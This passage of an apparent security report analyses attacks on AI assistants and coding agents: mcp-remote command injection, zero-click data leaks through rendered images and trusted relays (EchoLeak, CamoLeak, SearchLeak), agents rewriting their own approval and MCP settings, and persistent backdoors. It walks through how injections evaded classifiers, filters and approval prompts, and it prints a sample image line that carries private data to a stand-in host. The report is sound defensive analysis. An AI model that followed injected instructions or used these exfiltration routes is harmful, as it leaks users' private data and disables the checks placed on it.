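Browser makers can also block these routes. Chrome now asks the user before it lets a public website contact a local address. Chrome for Developers (2025) announced the prompt for testing in June 2025 and said it didn't yet cover WebSockets. Chrome 142 made the prompt standard for ordinary requests in October 2025 (Visualware, 2026). The OpenClaw attack used a WebSocket, so Chrome 144, the current version in January 2026, showed no prompt.

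Chromium's *Intent to Ship* (2026), a notice posted on 19 February by the open-source project behind Chrome, announced that the prompt would extend to WebSockets. According to Visualware, the change came in Chrome 147, in April, and other Chromium-based browsers such as Edge and Brave have the same restriction, but Firefox and Safari do not. The prompt should also help against DNS rebinding, because it depends on the IP address the browser actually connects to.

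Chromium's permission prompt has the same weakness as the trust dialogs in coding agents, since users may not know whether a website has a good reason to contact their computer. Some websites do, including that of Visualware, a maker of network-testing software that published its page because the prompt affected its browser-based tests. An earlier Chromium plan, Private Network Access, would have required local software to opt in before it received requests from websites. Chromium replaced this plan with the prompt, according to its *Intent to Ship* notice. Companies can also turn the restriction off for all websites. Developers of local agent tools therefore can't rely on the browser to protect their users.

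### mcp-remote: a sign-in address that ran as a command

Many early host applications, including Claude Desktop and Cursor, could connect only to local servers. The open-source program mcp-remote, maintained by Glen Maddern, gave them access to remote ones. The host application starts mcp-remote as if it were a local STDIO server, and mcp-remote forwards messages to the remote server over HTTP. The user only has to add the remote server's address to the configuration file.

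If the remote server requires a login, mcp-remote requests the address of the sign-in page from the server and passes it to the operating system to open. An address that begins with `https` opens in the browser, but one that begins with `file` refers to something on the user's own disk, and opening it can start a program. Because mcp-remote didn't check how the address began, a malicious server could reply with the location of a program instead of a sign-in page (CVE-2025-6514).

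On Windows, the flaw let an attacker run commands with full control over their arguments. mcp-remote opened addresses with a library that put them into a command for PowerShell, a Windows command shell. PowerShell runs certain expressions inside text, so a server could hide a command in the address. JFrog's *Critical RCE Vulnerability in mcp-remote* (2025) reports that the researchers could at first start programs but not give them arguments, because the code that processed the address replaced every space. The code kept the spaces if the address began with a scheme that doesn't exist, so the researchers used one to run complete commands. On macOS and Linux, the library doesn't use a shell, and the researchers could only start programs with limited control over the arguments.

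All this happens while the host application is connecting, before the user sees a sign-in page or the model reads anything. The server doesn't have to be malicious, because if the user entered an `http://` address, the connection is unencrypted and someone on the same network could replace the server's reply.

JFrog's advisory credits Or Peles with discovering the flaw, gives it a score of 9.6 and lists mcp-remote versions 0.0.5 to 0.1.15 as affected. Maddern fixed it in version 0.1.16. CISA recorded no exploitation when JFrog published its findings on 9 July 2025, according to MITRE's *OS command injection in mcp-remote when connecting to untrusted MCP servers*.

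mcp-remote's developers were not the only ones who could have added a check. The code that received the sign-in address belonged to the official TypeScript SDK, which confirmed that the text was a valid address but not that it led to a web page. Nor would a check on the scheme have been enough by itself. JFrog's researchers also started a program with an address that began with `http` and had a PowerShell expression in the middle. To block this version, the client also has to open the address without a shell, the same remedy as for the shell injection in bytebot.

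A later flaw in MCP Inspector combined both directions of attack. When a developer connected it to an untrusted remote server, the server could send a redirect address that ran a script inside the Inspector's web interface. The script could then use the proxy to run commands on the developer's machine. The session token from version 0.14.1 did not prevent this, because the interface already had it. Version 0.16.6 checks the address more strictly, according to GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/@Modelcontextprotocol/Inspector package*.

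### What the checks cost

Requiring a token on a local port adds very little work for the user if the software's developer plans for it. The Inspector prints a link that already contains the token, so the user clicks the link instead of copying the token. Lumelsky notes that Jupyter does the same. An MCP server's token takes more work, because the user has to enter it in every host application that connects. A token also protects against other programs and other users on the same computer, which a check on browser headers doesn't do, because programs other than browsers can put anything in those headers.

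Host and Origin checks can block people who reach a server under an unexpected name, for instance through a company gateway. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-11624* (2026) describes a server that already had a list of permitted origins and whose developers added a list of permitted hosts in version 0.25.0. To avoid breaking existing setups, they let both lists accept everything by default and had the server print a warning when it starts. Anyone who overlooks the warning is therefore as exposed as before.

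The TypeScript SDK makes a better compromise by turning the check on automatically when a server listens on `localhost`, where the developer knows the legitimate names in advance and few users will notice the restriction. This default doesn't protect a server on a company's internal network, which a rebinding attack can also reach through an employee's browser. The administrator still has to list the permitted names for that server.

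Checking the scheme of a sign-in address has almost no downside, since a sign-in page is always a web page. Model Context Protocol's security guidance recommends that clients require `https` for all such addresses, except `localhost` during development. Requiring `https` would also prevent the interception attack on mcp-remote. Some company servers still use plain `http` on an internal network, and their users would have to set up encryption first.

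## Data leaks through displayed images and links

When a browser displays a model's answer in a chat application, it requests any images the answer contains. A prompt injection can make the model include an image whose address points to the attacker's website and contains a password. When the browser requests that image, it sends the password to the attacker.

### How an image's address carries data

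Most models write their answers in Markdown, which uses ordinary characters for formatting, such as asterisks for bold text and brackets for links and images. The host application converts the Markdown into the formatted text that the user sees.

Suppose Ana asks for a summary of the notes folder. One of the notes, pasted from a stranger's email, tells AI assistants to end with a calendar icon and put the week's appointments in the icon's address. The model might write:

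```text
You have one appointment this week, on Tuesday.

![calendar icon](https://pictures.example/icon.png?note=dentist-tuesday)
```

The leak then takes four steps:

1. The application recognises the last line as an image and requests it from `pictures.example`.
2. The request includes the whole address. Websites normally use the part after the question mark for details such as the size of a picture, but it can hold any text.
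3. The server at `pictures.example` records the request in its log, where its owner can read "dentist-tuesday".
4. The server sends back an ordinary icon, so Ana notices nothing.

The application fetches the image to display it, so Ana doesn't have to click anything. An ordinary link can send the same data, but only if the user clicks it. The data can also go in other parts of the address, including the host name, as Microsoft (2025) explains in an article on its defences against prompt injection.

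Researchers call such an attack "zero-click" if the victim doesn't have to open or click anything the attacker sent. The victim usually still has to ask the assistant a question, as Ana did.

### EchoLeak: one email against four defences

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their emails, files and chats for relevant passages and adding these to the model's context. Only employees can use a company's Copilot, but it also searches emails they receive from people outside the company.

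In January 2025, Aim Labs, the research department of Aim Security, reported to Microsoft that an outsider could steal private data with a single email (CVE-2025-32711). *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes the attack.

Copilot first had to retrieve the email while answering an unrelated question. The researchers assumed that it looks for passages close in meaning to the question, so they wrote a long email with sections on common office subjects, such as staff onboarding and leave of absence. Each section repeated the same instructions, which told the reader to add the most sensitive information available to a web address. The email then had to get past four defences.

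Microsoft used a classifier to detect text written to manipulate an AI. The researchers got their email past it by phrasing the instructions as if they were meant for the employee and never mentioning AI or Copilot. This worked because a request to a colleague and a request to an assistant can use the same words. Ravia adds that developers have few good examples of real injections to train such classifiers on.

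**Link removal.** Copilot deleted links and images that pointed outside the company from its answers. But Markdown has a second way to write an image, with the address on a separate line:

```text
![calendar icon][1]

[1]: https://pictures.example/icon.png
```

The filter didn't recognise this form, but the program that displayed the answer did. Microsoft could have avoided the mismatch by checking for images after converting the Markdown, when both forms look the same.

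Copilot's web page had a Content Security Policy, a set of rules that limits which sites the browser may load content from. For images, the policy allowed about 30 domains, mostly Microsoft's own, so the browser blocked image requests to the researchers' server.

The researchers therefore looked for a permitted site that would contact their server. A function in SharePoint, Microsoft's service for shared documents, would have worked, but only if the victim first accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A function in Teams, Microsoft's chat program, required no invitation and fetched any web address it received. The researchers put their own address, with the stolen data, inside a Teams address. The browser contacted Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams passed the data on to the researchers' server.

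Copilot normally names the emails it used for an answer, and seeing the attacker's email named might have made the employee suspicious. But the email contained an instruction to its reader never to mention it, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot followed that instruction.

Microsoft began repairing the flaw in April 2025 and fully fixed it in May, according to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025). Microsoft runs Copilot on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft rated the flaw's severity at 9.3, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it at 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft knew of no attacks on customers.

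Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click vulnerability in a major AI application. Reddy and Gujral call it the first known case of someone "weaponizing" a prompt injection to steal data from a product in use, which is misleading because only researchers are known to have used it. The programmer Simon Willison (2025) regards it as an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. One of them was Microsoft 365 Copilot itself. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes a flaw found there in February 2024 that let an email make Copilot search the inbox and hide the results in a link as invisible characters. Microsoft fixed it that July. In that attack, the victim had to click the link, whereas EchoLeak sent the data automatically.

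### CamoLeak: a message spelled out in images

GitHub, Microsoft's code-sharing site, has an assistant called Copilot Chat that answers questions about projects. GitHub fixed an earlier leak in Copilot Chat by blocking images from untrusted domains, according to Willison. In June 2025 a researcher at the software-security company Legit Security found a way to leak data through GitHub's own image service. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* gives the flaw a severity score of 9.6.

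The attacker starts by proposing a change to a project and adding a comment to the description. GitHub lets authors hide such comments from visitors, but Copilot Chat read them. If another user asked Copilot to explain the change, it could follow instructions in the comment with that user's permissions and open private projects that the attacker couldn't.

The attacker still needed a way to get the data out. GitHub's Content Security Policy blocks images from domains that GitHub doesn't own, but project pages can still display outside images through Camo, a GitHub server that fetches them and passes them on. When a developer saves a page containing an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a Camo address that includes a cryptographic signature. Camo refuses any address without a valid signature.

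This design would have stopped the method used in EchoLeak. A model can't calculate GitHub's signature, so it can't write a working Camo address that contains stolen text. The researcher got around this by preparing all the addresses in advance:

1. The researcher set up a web server that answered every request with a transparent image one pixel wide.
2. Using a public GitHub function, the researcher obtained a signed Camo address for each letter and symbol.
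3. The hidden comment contained this list and asked Copilot to write out private text as a series of images.
4. The victim's browser loaded the images in order through Camo, and the server's log spelled out the text.

To leak the word "notes", Copilot would display five invisible images, one for each letter. A random number at the end of each image's address made the browser request the image again for a repeated letter instead of using a saved copy.

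In the demonstration, Copilot leaked the description of an undisclosed vulnerability from a private project. The researcher also had it search the victim's code for cloud access keys and send out what it found.

Camo's signatures worked as designed, since GitHub had signed every address. But the attack encoded the secret in the choice and order of the images, so no single address would have looked suspicious. This method needs a separate request for every character, which makes it practical for stealing passwords and keys but slow for a large body of code. Microsoft describes the smallest version of this kind of leak, in which an attacker learns one bit of information from whether an agent calls a tool.

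By 14 August 2025 GitHub had stopped displaying any images in Copilot Chat. Legit Security reports no criminal use of the flaw and gives no CVE number for it. CVE-2025-59145, which is sometimes linked to CamoLeak, belongs to an unrelated incident. NVD's *CVE-2025-59145 Detail* describes how an attacker took over the publishing account for the JavaScript package color-name and added malware to the package.

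### Other requests that software makes automatically

Images are only one reason software contacts an address without a click. Some chat applications draw diagrams from a description that the model writes. If the description can include outside images, the drawing program may fetch an address that the application's image filter never checked. Code editors may also download the schema for a settings file when they open the file.

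Messaging programs fetch the title and picture of a linked page to show a preview. If an agent posts a link with private data in its address, fetching the preview sends the data to the linked site before anyone clicks. Reddy and Gujral report that the Teams function in EchoLeak was part of a preview service.

Data can leak through a DNS lookup, before any connection to the attacker's web server. To load an image from `dentist-tuesday.pictures.example`, a computer first has to look up the IP address for that name. The query normally reaches a name server chosen by the owner of `pictures.example`, who can read the first part of the name, `dentist-tuesday`. A firewall that only blocks the subsequent web connection doesn't prevent this leak, so anyone who runs an agent in a sandbox without internet access has to restrict DNS lookups as well. A host name can't exceed 253 characters, so an attacker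 would need several lookups to extract a longer text.

Agents that browse the web can leak data without displaying anything. In an attack called ShadowLeak, an email with hidden instructions made ChatGPT's Deep Research feature find private data in a Gmail inbox and visit a web address containing that data. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* points out that the request came from OpenAI's servers, so the victim's browser and their company's monitoring software might not have recorded it. The researchers reported that the attack worked every time in repeated tests.

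A tool that only reads web pages can still leak data through the addresses it requests. In *The Memory Heist*, Paul (2026) got Claude to use its built-in web browsing to reveal a user's name, employer and home town, all drawn from earlier conversations. Microsoft's Copilot for personal use had a similar flaw, in which a single click on a link could make it read a connected Gmail account and send the contents out by "summarising" a web address. The security company Varonis reports in *CoSnitch* (2026) that it disclosed the flaw in December 2025 and that Microsoft patched it on 18 August 2026. Varonis saw no evidence of attacks.

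### Bing as a relay in 2026

The list of permitted image sources that Aim Labs published with EchoLeak also included Bing, Microsoft's search engine. A year later, Varonis used Bing to get data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes the attack (CVE-2026-42824), which began with a link to Copilot's search page. When the victim clicked the link, Copilot treated the question it contained as instructions.

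By then Microsoft had Copilot mark its answers as code, so that the browser would show an image's address as plain text instead of loading the image. But Copilot marked an answer only after finishing it. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived, so it had already requested the image.

Bing relayed the data, as Teams had in EchoLeak. Its image search accepts the address of a picture and fetches the picture to analyse it. The browser was allowed to contact Bing, which then requested an address on Varonis' server that contained the title of one of the victim's emails. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, fixed it and said there was no evidence of malicious use, according to The Next Web.

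On 3 December 2026 the team behind EchoLeak, now called Cato AI Labs, published three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot under the name ReLeak. Each attack used an email that could remain unread and worked once the user asked Copilot a question that retrieved it. One attack sent data out in an image address, again through Bing, according to Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026). Another used a link to a saved file, and the third used code that Copilot ran. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) notes that a sandbox failed to block outgoing traffic, although its documentation said it would. Microsoft patched the three routes on 17 September, 11 November and 15 November, and Cato knows of no real attacks that used them.

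After EchoLeak, Microsoft wrote that it responds to such reports by fixing the reported flaw and looking for variants. Its search evidently missed Bing, even though Bing was on the published list. Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made" (quoted in Faisal, 2026, *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*).

### Why a trusted relay defeats an allowlist

A Content Security Policy controls which sites the browser contacts, but not what those sites do next. If a permitted site accepts a web address and fetches it, the request for that address comes from the site's own servers, where the policy doesn't apply. This is server-side request forgery (SSRF), but the attacker uses it to reach their own server instead of an internal one.

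These relays are hard to remove because they often exist to fetch URLs. An image search has to fetch the picture it analyses, and a preview service the page it previews. Blocking internal addresses, the usual defence against SSRF, doesn't help because the attacker's server has an ordinary public address.

The entries in Copilot's list were also broad. An entry for all of Bing permits every function on the site, including any that Microsoft adds later. The entry for SharePoint covered sites that customers create, and an attacker can be a customer. Varonis recommends treating any permitted domain that fetches URLs supplied by users as a possible route for leaking data. A team maintaining such a list would therefore have to check what each site does, and check again as the sites change.

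### Comparing the repairs

GitHub responded to CamoLeak by no longer displaying images, which is the most dependable way to prevent leaks through them. This works whatever the model writes, and a coding assistant is nearly as useful without images. Amazon similarly stopped making links clickable in its Q assistant for businesses after researchers found that it could leak data through them, according to *Trust No AI*.

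However, the ban has to cover everything the application can display. In June 2026 OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that limits outgoing requests to reduce data theft. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that the security company Check Point found a way around it through ChatGPT's preview of web pages. The preview ran in a sandbox, but a page could open a pop-up window that the sandbox didn't restrict. In the desktop application, an attacker could steal chats this way without the user clicking anything. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026. Atlassian's assistant, Rovo, also leaked company documents despite controls that let organisations restrict web searches, according to PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*.

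An allowlist lets the application display images from approved sites, but it is safe only if none of those sites relays requests or lets outsiders see them. The simplest safe version permits a single server that holds the application's own icons and pictures and never fetches anything else. This would suit an assistant that displays charts it has made itself, but not one that needs to show pictures from the web.

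Reddy and Gujral, who ran no experiments, list a proxy with signed addresses among the measures that should prevent zero-click leaks, but CamoLeak went through such a proxy. The addresses in Reddy and Gujral's version would also expire. An attacker would then have to keep renewing the list of letters, but the method would still work.

User confirmation works best for actions that people understand. Copilot in Outlook can draft an email, but the user has to approve the text and send it. Asking before loading an image is less useful, since few people could tell whether the image's long address contains encoded data. In SearchLeak, employees would have seen a prompt to approve a request to Bing, and most would have allowed it.

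The other approach is to keep private data and untrusted text apart. Willison describes the danger as a "lethal trifecta" of access to private data, exposure to malicious text and a way to send data out. Blocking images removes only one way to send data out, and ReLeak used three. Reddy and Gujral point out that EchoLeak would have failed at the start if Copilot had never used emails from outsiders to answer questions about internal matters.

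Labelling outside text as untrusted is a weaker defence than separating it. Microsoft marks untrusted passages and tells the model not to follow instructions in them, but it calls this a probabilistic defence, meaning that it makes an attack less likely without ruling it out. Real separation requires the application to withhold the text from the model or restrict what the model can do after reading it. FIDES, a system developed by Microsoft researchers, enforces such limits through information-flow control, which tracks where data came from and where it may go.

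Separating external text from internal text limits Copilot more than removing images does, because many useful questions need both. For example, an employee may ask whether the company can meet a delivery date that a customer requested by email. Copilot could still read the email and the internal schedule together, as long as the application displayed the answer as plain text and disabled web access and other outgoing tools until the conversation no longer contained the customer's words.

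## Agents that edit the settings governing them

Many products let a coding agent create and change files anywhere in the workspace, the folder the user has open, without asking each time, because constant prompts would be tiresome and most files do nothing until someone runs them. Settings files are riskier because the code editor or the agent reads them and may act on a change immediately.

If an agent can edit the settings that govern it, an attacker can use a prompt injection to make it write whatever setting the attacker needs. These settings are often in the same files that a malicious project brings with it, but here the project can be the user's own and initially harmless. The agent adds the dangerous line later, after it reads a stranger's web page or message.

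### Copilot: approval prompts that the agent could turn off

GitHub Copilot has an agent mode in Visual Studio Code, Microsoft's code editor. In mid-2025 the agent needed the user's approval to run commands but not to write files in the workspace. It saved its changes straight to disk, whereas many other editors show them to the user first. *GitHub Copilot*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, explains how an attacker could use these unapproved writes to run commands (CVE-2025-53773).

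VS Code keeps a project's settings in `.vscode/settings.json`. One of them, `chat.tools.autoApprove`, turned off all of Copilot's confirmations. It was experimental, but the standard version of the editor included it. The attack took four steps:

1. The attacker hid instructions in something Copilot would read, such as a source file, a web page or a tool's reply.
2. Copilot followed them and added the setting to the project's settings file, creating the file if necessary.
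3. The setting took effect immediately.
4. Copilot ran the attacker's command without asking.

The approval prompt worked while it was on, but the agent could turn it off by editing a file. The attack worked on Windows, macOS and Linux. In one demonstration it opened the calculator, and in another it downloaded malware that connected the computer to a server the researcher controlled.

The researcher also wrote the instructions in invisible characters, which a developer reading the file would not see. This version worked several times but was unreliable. Models often refuse such instructions, and VS Code usually warns about the characters. According to the post, an attacker could also use the access to plant the same instructions in the developer's other projects, and colleagues who downloaded those projects could spread them further.

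Embrace The Red reported the flaw on 29 June 2025. Microsoft replied a few weeks later that it was already tracking the problem, and fixed it in its August updates. Markus Vervier of Persistent Security and the researcher Ari Marzouk had found it independently. STAR Labs' *GitHub Copilot and Visual Studio* (2025) reproduces Microsoft's assessment, which gives a severity score of 7.8 and records no exploitation.

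Copilot later had a check that guarded sensitive files such as `settings.json`. According to GitHub's *Sensitive file editing guard bypass* (2025), the check applied when the agent changed an existing file but not when it created a new one. On the same day in November 2025, GitHub published a second advisory under the same title, about file paths that the editing tools had failed to validate. Both flaws affected version 0.32.4 and earlier of Copilot Chat, the extension that provides agent mode. Version 0.32.5 fixes both.

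### Cursor: a server that started before the user could refuse

Cursor started a new MCP server as soon as its entry appeared in the configuration file, so an attacker didn't need to turn off any prompts. *When Public Prompts Turn Into Local Shells* (Abu, 2025) describes how Aim Labs, the team behind EchoLeak, exploited this (CVE-2025-54135).

In the demonstration, a user had connected Cursor to the workplace chat service Slack through an MCP server. An attacker posted a message in a public channel, and the user then asked Cursor to summarise the user's Slack messages. The attacker's message led the agent to "improve" the MCP configuration by adding an entry containing a command. Cursor showed this edit as a suggestion that the user could reject, but it had already saved the edit to disk, so the command ran before the user could respond.

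According to the official record, NVD's *CVE-2025-54135 Detail* (2025), Cursor required approval to change an existing dotfile (a file whose name starts with a dot and which usually holds settings) but not to create one. The attack therefore worked if the project had no `.cursor/mcp.json` yet. Copilot's check had the same gap a few months later. Abu doesn't mention that the file had to be missing and writes that Cursor ran any new entry without confirmation.

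Aim Labs reported the flaw on 7 July 2025, and Cursor's developers added a fix to their code the next day. Abu gives the fixed version as 1.3, but NVD gives 1.3.9, so 1.3.9 or later is the safer choice. SecurityWeek reports a severity score of 8.6. The flaw's record listed no known exploitation when it appeared in August (GCVE, 2025).

In Cursor's other flaw from that summer, CVE-2025-54136, a collaborator changed the command of an approved server. In both cases, Cursor ran a command that the user had not approved. Cursor would have stopped both attacks if it had asked the user to approve the exact command before starting a server.

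### Windsurf: an edit whose contents stayed hidden

OX Security reported a similar flaw in Windsurf as part of its April 2026 disclosure (CVE-2026-30615). In OX Security's account, the victim visits the attacker's website and copies a prompt that looks useful. When Windsurf requests the page, the site returns different content containing malicious instructions, so the victim can't find them by reading the page in a browser. The agent then proposes an edit to the MCP configuration without showing what will change, and makes the edit. Windsurf immediately starts the new server.

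This attack requires the victim to visit a website and copy a prompt from it, which makes it harder to carry out than EchoLeak, where an unopened email was enough. OX Security still calls it "zero-click" and says that Windsurf was the only editor it could exploit without any user interaction. That description is accurate only after Windsurf reads the page, when no approval prompt interrupts the attack.

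NVD's *CVE-2026-30615 Detail* (2026) lists version 1.9544.26 as vulnerable, while OX Security lists all versions. Neither identifies a version that fixes the flaw, and OX's status table marks it as reported, not patched. The CVE record listed no known exploitation, according to Arawa (2026). NVD notes that the malicious entry can remain in the configuration, which would give the attacker persistence.

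### IDEsaster: old editor features with a new user

The settings in these three cases control the agent itself. In December 2025 Ari Marzouk, one of the discoverers of the Copilot flaw, published research on the settings of the code editor that the agent runs in. The research is called IDEsaster, after integrated development environments (IDEs), which are code editors with built-in tools.

The Hacker News reports that over six months Marzouk found more than 30 flaws in products including Cursor, Windsurf, Copilot, Amazon's Kiro, Zed, Roo Code, Cline and JetBrains' Junie. Twenty-four of the flaws received CVE numbers. Several of the attacks worked on every AI code editor Marzouk tested.

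Code editors have long had settings that can start a program or download a file. This was a modest risk when developers edited the settings themselves. According to Marzouk, the makers of AI coding tools treated these features as "inherently safe because they've been there for years" and didn't reconsider them when they added an agent that could write the settings.

**Running a command through a program path.** VS Code can check PHP, a language used for websites, by running the PHP program installed on the computer. People install PHP in different places, so a setting tells the editor where to find it. An attacker can use this setting in three steps:

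1. A prompt injection reaches the model through a pasted web address, hidden text or an MCP server's reply.
2. The agent changes the setting so that it points to a file containing the attacker's code.
3. When the editor next checks a PHP file, it runs the attacker's code instead of PHP.

Because the agent edits only a text file and the editor starts the program, the user never sees the prompt that asks for approval before the agent runs a command. Attackers could also exploit a setting that tells the editor where to find Git.

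**Leaking data through a schema.** A JSON file can include the address of a schema, which describes the entries the file may contain. The editor downloads the schema so that it can suggest entries and mark errors. An ordinary settings file might begin like this:

```json
{
  "$schema": "https://schemas.example/notes.json"
}
```

In the attack, the agent reads a sensitive file, such as one that holds access keys. It then writes a JSON file whose schema address points to the attacker's website and contains the keys. The editor requests the schema from that address, and the attacker reads the keys in the website's log, as with the images in chat applications. In some products, the agent needed only its normal tools for reading and writing files. In others, a flaw in the search tool helped it read the sensitive file.

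The third group of attacks used workspace files, which VS Code provides for working in several folders at once. A workspace file lists the folders and can also contain settings that override those in other files, so a vendor that protects only `settings.json` leaves another way to change the same settings.

The table shows how The Hacker News assigns the flaws to the three features. A dash means the site doesn't list the product under that feature.

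| Product | Schema from the web | Program path | Workspace file |
|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub Copilot | No CVE | CVE-2025-53773 | CVE-2025-64660 |
| Cursor | CVE-2025-49150 | CVE-2025-54130 | CVE-2025-61590 |
| Roo Code | CVE-2025-53097 | CVE-2025-53536 | CVE-2025-58372 |
| Junie | CVE-2025-58335 | – | – |
| Zed | – | CVE-2025-55012 | – |
| Kiro | No CVE | – | – |
| Claude Code | Security warning added | Security warning added | – |

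A Copilot agent that can write to `settings.json` can change either the approval setting or a program path, and CVE-2025-53773 covers both changes.

The ten CVE numbers in the table cover only three editor features, so the total of 24 is a poor guide to how many different mistakes developers made. Some of the repetition comes from shared code. Cursor and Windsurf are built on VS Code, and Copilot and Roo Code run inside it, so all four share its settings. But Zed and JetBrains make their own editors, and their products had similar flaws.

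The attacks that run commands require the agent to write files without approval, which many products allow by default inside the workspace. The attacks then work without any action from the user, even reopening the project. Microsoft gave the workspace-file flaw in Copilot a severity score of 8.0, released a fix and recorded no exploitation, according to STAR Labs' *GitHub Copilot and Visual Studio Code* (2025).

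### Mindgard's survey of coding tools

On 3 March 2026, Piotr Ryciak of Mindgard, a company that tests AI systems for security flaws, presented a broader survey at the [un]prompted conference. Mindgard had found 37 vulnerabilities in the products of more than 15 vendors, according to *[un]prompted 2026*, a summary of the conference talks. The affected products included Google's Gemini CLI and OpenAI's Codex.

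Mindgard's *Vibe Check* (2026) groups the attacks by what triggers them. Some require no action from the user, some require a single click, some run automatically, and some run only after a later event. By April 2026, vendors had fixed some of the flaws and were working on others.

Ugo Enyioha, a developer of the coding agent OpenCode, which was on Mindgard's list, explains in *37 Vulnerabilities Exposed Across 15 AI IDEs* that Mindgard reduced the 37 flaws to 25 recurring patterns. Only some of these patterns involve agents that edit settings. Others involve project files that run before the user has trusted a folder, or approvals that remain valid after a file changes.

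An attack on Kiro combined a configuration change with several other steps. The attacker used a folder's name as an instruction to open a file inside the folder and follow the directions there. Kiro's agent read the name while examining the project and obeyed. It then found an access key in another file, put the key in a web address and used a built-in Kiro feature to request that address. None of these steps would do much harm alone, and the attack worked whether or not the user had trusted the folder.

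Mindgard's total can't be added to Marzouk's, because both studied Cursor and Kiro and may have counted some of the same flaws. But two separate investigations found serious problems in most of the well-known coding tools within a few months, so the flaws were not limited to a few careless vendors.

Vendors have not always cooperated. The Hacker News (2026) reports that Mindgard asked Cursor for updates on another flaw in February, March and April and got no reply. Mindgard published the full details on 14 July, and Cursor responded publicly the next day. In the meantime, Cursor had published an advisory on a flaw reported by another company, Novee. That flaw let an attacker use Git hooks to escape Cursor's sandbox (CVE-2026-26268), and Cursor fixed it in version 2.5 in February.

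### Edits that the user approved

OX Security got agents to change the MCP configuration of coding tools. Only Windsurf received a CVE number for this, because several vendors don't count an edit that the user approved as a vulnerability. Anthropic told the researchers that the user is "given the opportunity to approve or deny the change", according to ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector for supply chain*.

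This rule is reasonable if the user can see the whole change and nothing happens until they answer. Someone who asked for a summary of Slack messages has a fair chance of noticing that the agent is trying to add a server with an unfamiliar command, because the edit has nothing to do with their request. A trust dialog for a whole folder gives them much less information to judge by.

The older version of Cursor broke this rule by applying the edit before the user answered, and Windsurf broke it by hiding the contents. The SymJack attack likewise disguised a settings change as an ordinary file copy. If a prompt hides or misdescribes the change, the user who approves it has not meaningfully consented, and vendors should treat the attack as a vulnerability.

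The problem is harder when a prompt shows the change accurately but looks like every other prompt. An agent may propose dozens of edits in an hour, and a tired developer could approve a new server entry along with the rest. Vendors could reduce this risk by showing such edits separately and stating that they will start a program. This would add few interruptions because agents seldom have a good reason to change their own settings.

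A white paper by Alex Plaskett of the security company NCC Group treats modes that skip approval checks as an accepted risk because vendors document them, according to Mitchell (2026) in *NCC Group maps security gaps across AI coding agents*. That argument works if the user turned the mode on. In the Copilot attack, the agent turned it on for an attacker, so the user had not accepted that risk.

### Which products now protect these files

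Copilot Chat 0.32.5 and later check new and changed files against a list of sensitive files and validate the file paths. Cursor has protected new MCP configuration files since version 1.3.9 or earlier, but researchers later found other files it left unprotected. Anthropic responded to Marzouk's findings about Claude Code with a security warning. No fix for CVE-2026-30615 in Windsurf is on record.

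Protecting a list of files works only if the list is complete, and a complete list is difficult to make. Besides the settings and workspace files, VS Code has `tasks.json`, which defines commands for the editor to run. JetBrains editors have their own settings file, and Git has hooks. Embrace The Red points out that many developers use several agents in the same project, so one agent could add a malicious server to another's configuration. Each vendor's list would therefore have to include its competitors' settings files.

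The protection also has to cover every tool that can reach the files. Mindgard describes how the agent in Google's code editor Antigravity tried to open a protected file of passwords and keys. The file-reading tool blocked the attempt, so the agent used a terminal command instead. Agents can get around a write restriction in the same way if the restriction applies only to the editing tool. Plaskett's paper reports that researchers have repeatedly got tools meant only for reading to write files or run commands.

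A sandbox can block writes from all of an agent's tools, but it must also cover the settings files. Enyioha reports that Codex's sandbox restricted the agent's own tool calls but not the MCP servers that Codex started. In the agents that Plaskett examined, hooks also often run outside the sandbox. An agent that can add a server or hook to its settings can therefore run a program without the limits that apply to the agent itself.

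## Backdoors that survive the session

When a user closes a coding agent, the model's context disappears, but every file that the agent wrote stays on the disk. If the software reads one of those files the next time it starts, an attacker who controlled the agent for a minute can regain control days later, even if the user has since closed the malicious web page or deleted the malicious project.

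### Where agent software keeps things it uses again

Five kinds of stored item are useful to an attacker. In the file names below, `~` stands for the user's home folder.

| Stored item | Example | When it takes effect |
|---|---|---|
| Global tool configuration | `~/.codex/config.toml`, where Codex lists its MCP servers | Whenever the agent starts, in any project |
| Instruction files | `AGENTS.md`, `CLAUDE.md` | When the agent starts in that folder and, with some agents, in folders inside it |
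| Startup hooks | Commands that Claude Code runs when a session begins | In every session that the settings file covers |
| Stored memory | Facts that ChatGPT saves about its user | In every new conversation |
| Extensions | The Claude Code extension for code editors | Whenever the editor loads it |

Configuration entries, hooks and extensions contain commands or code that runs without any decision by the model. Instruction files and memories are text, so a backdoor in them works only if the model follows it. Such a backdoor is easier to overlook, though, because a paragraph recommending a package doesn't look like malware.

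An attacker can plant instruction files in several ways. For example, NVIDIA's security testers found that a malicious dependency (a package that a project relies on) could insert AGENTS.md instructions for Codex. As NVIDIA notes, such an attacker can already run some code, but the planted file also lets them influence what the agent does afterwards.

An entry inside a project is less dangerous than one that applies to the whole machine. In Check Point Research's attack on Cursor, for example, the altered command ran only when the victim opened that project, and a colleague could find the change in the project's history.

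A global entry runs no matter which project the user opens, and in some programs it runs before they open any. It isn't in any project's change history, so no colleague reviews it. It remains after the user deletes the malicious project, and it still runs if they refuse to trust the next project they open.

Instruction files can also affect more than one project. *AGENTS.md im Downloads-Ordner kapert Agenten* (Cornelißen, 2026) reports that Claude Code has read AGENTS.md files since September 2026. Claude Code looks in the folder where the user starts it and in every folder above, skipping any that has a CLAUDE.md. A file in the home folder could therefore influence nearly all of a user's projects.

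### Antigravity: one project that affected every later launch
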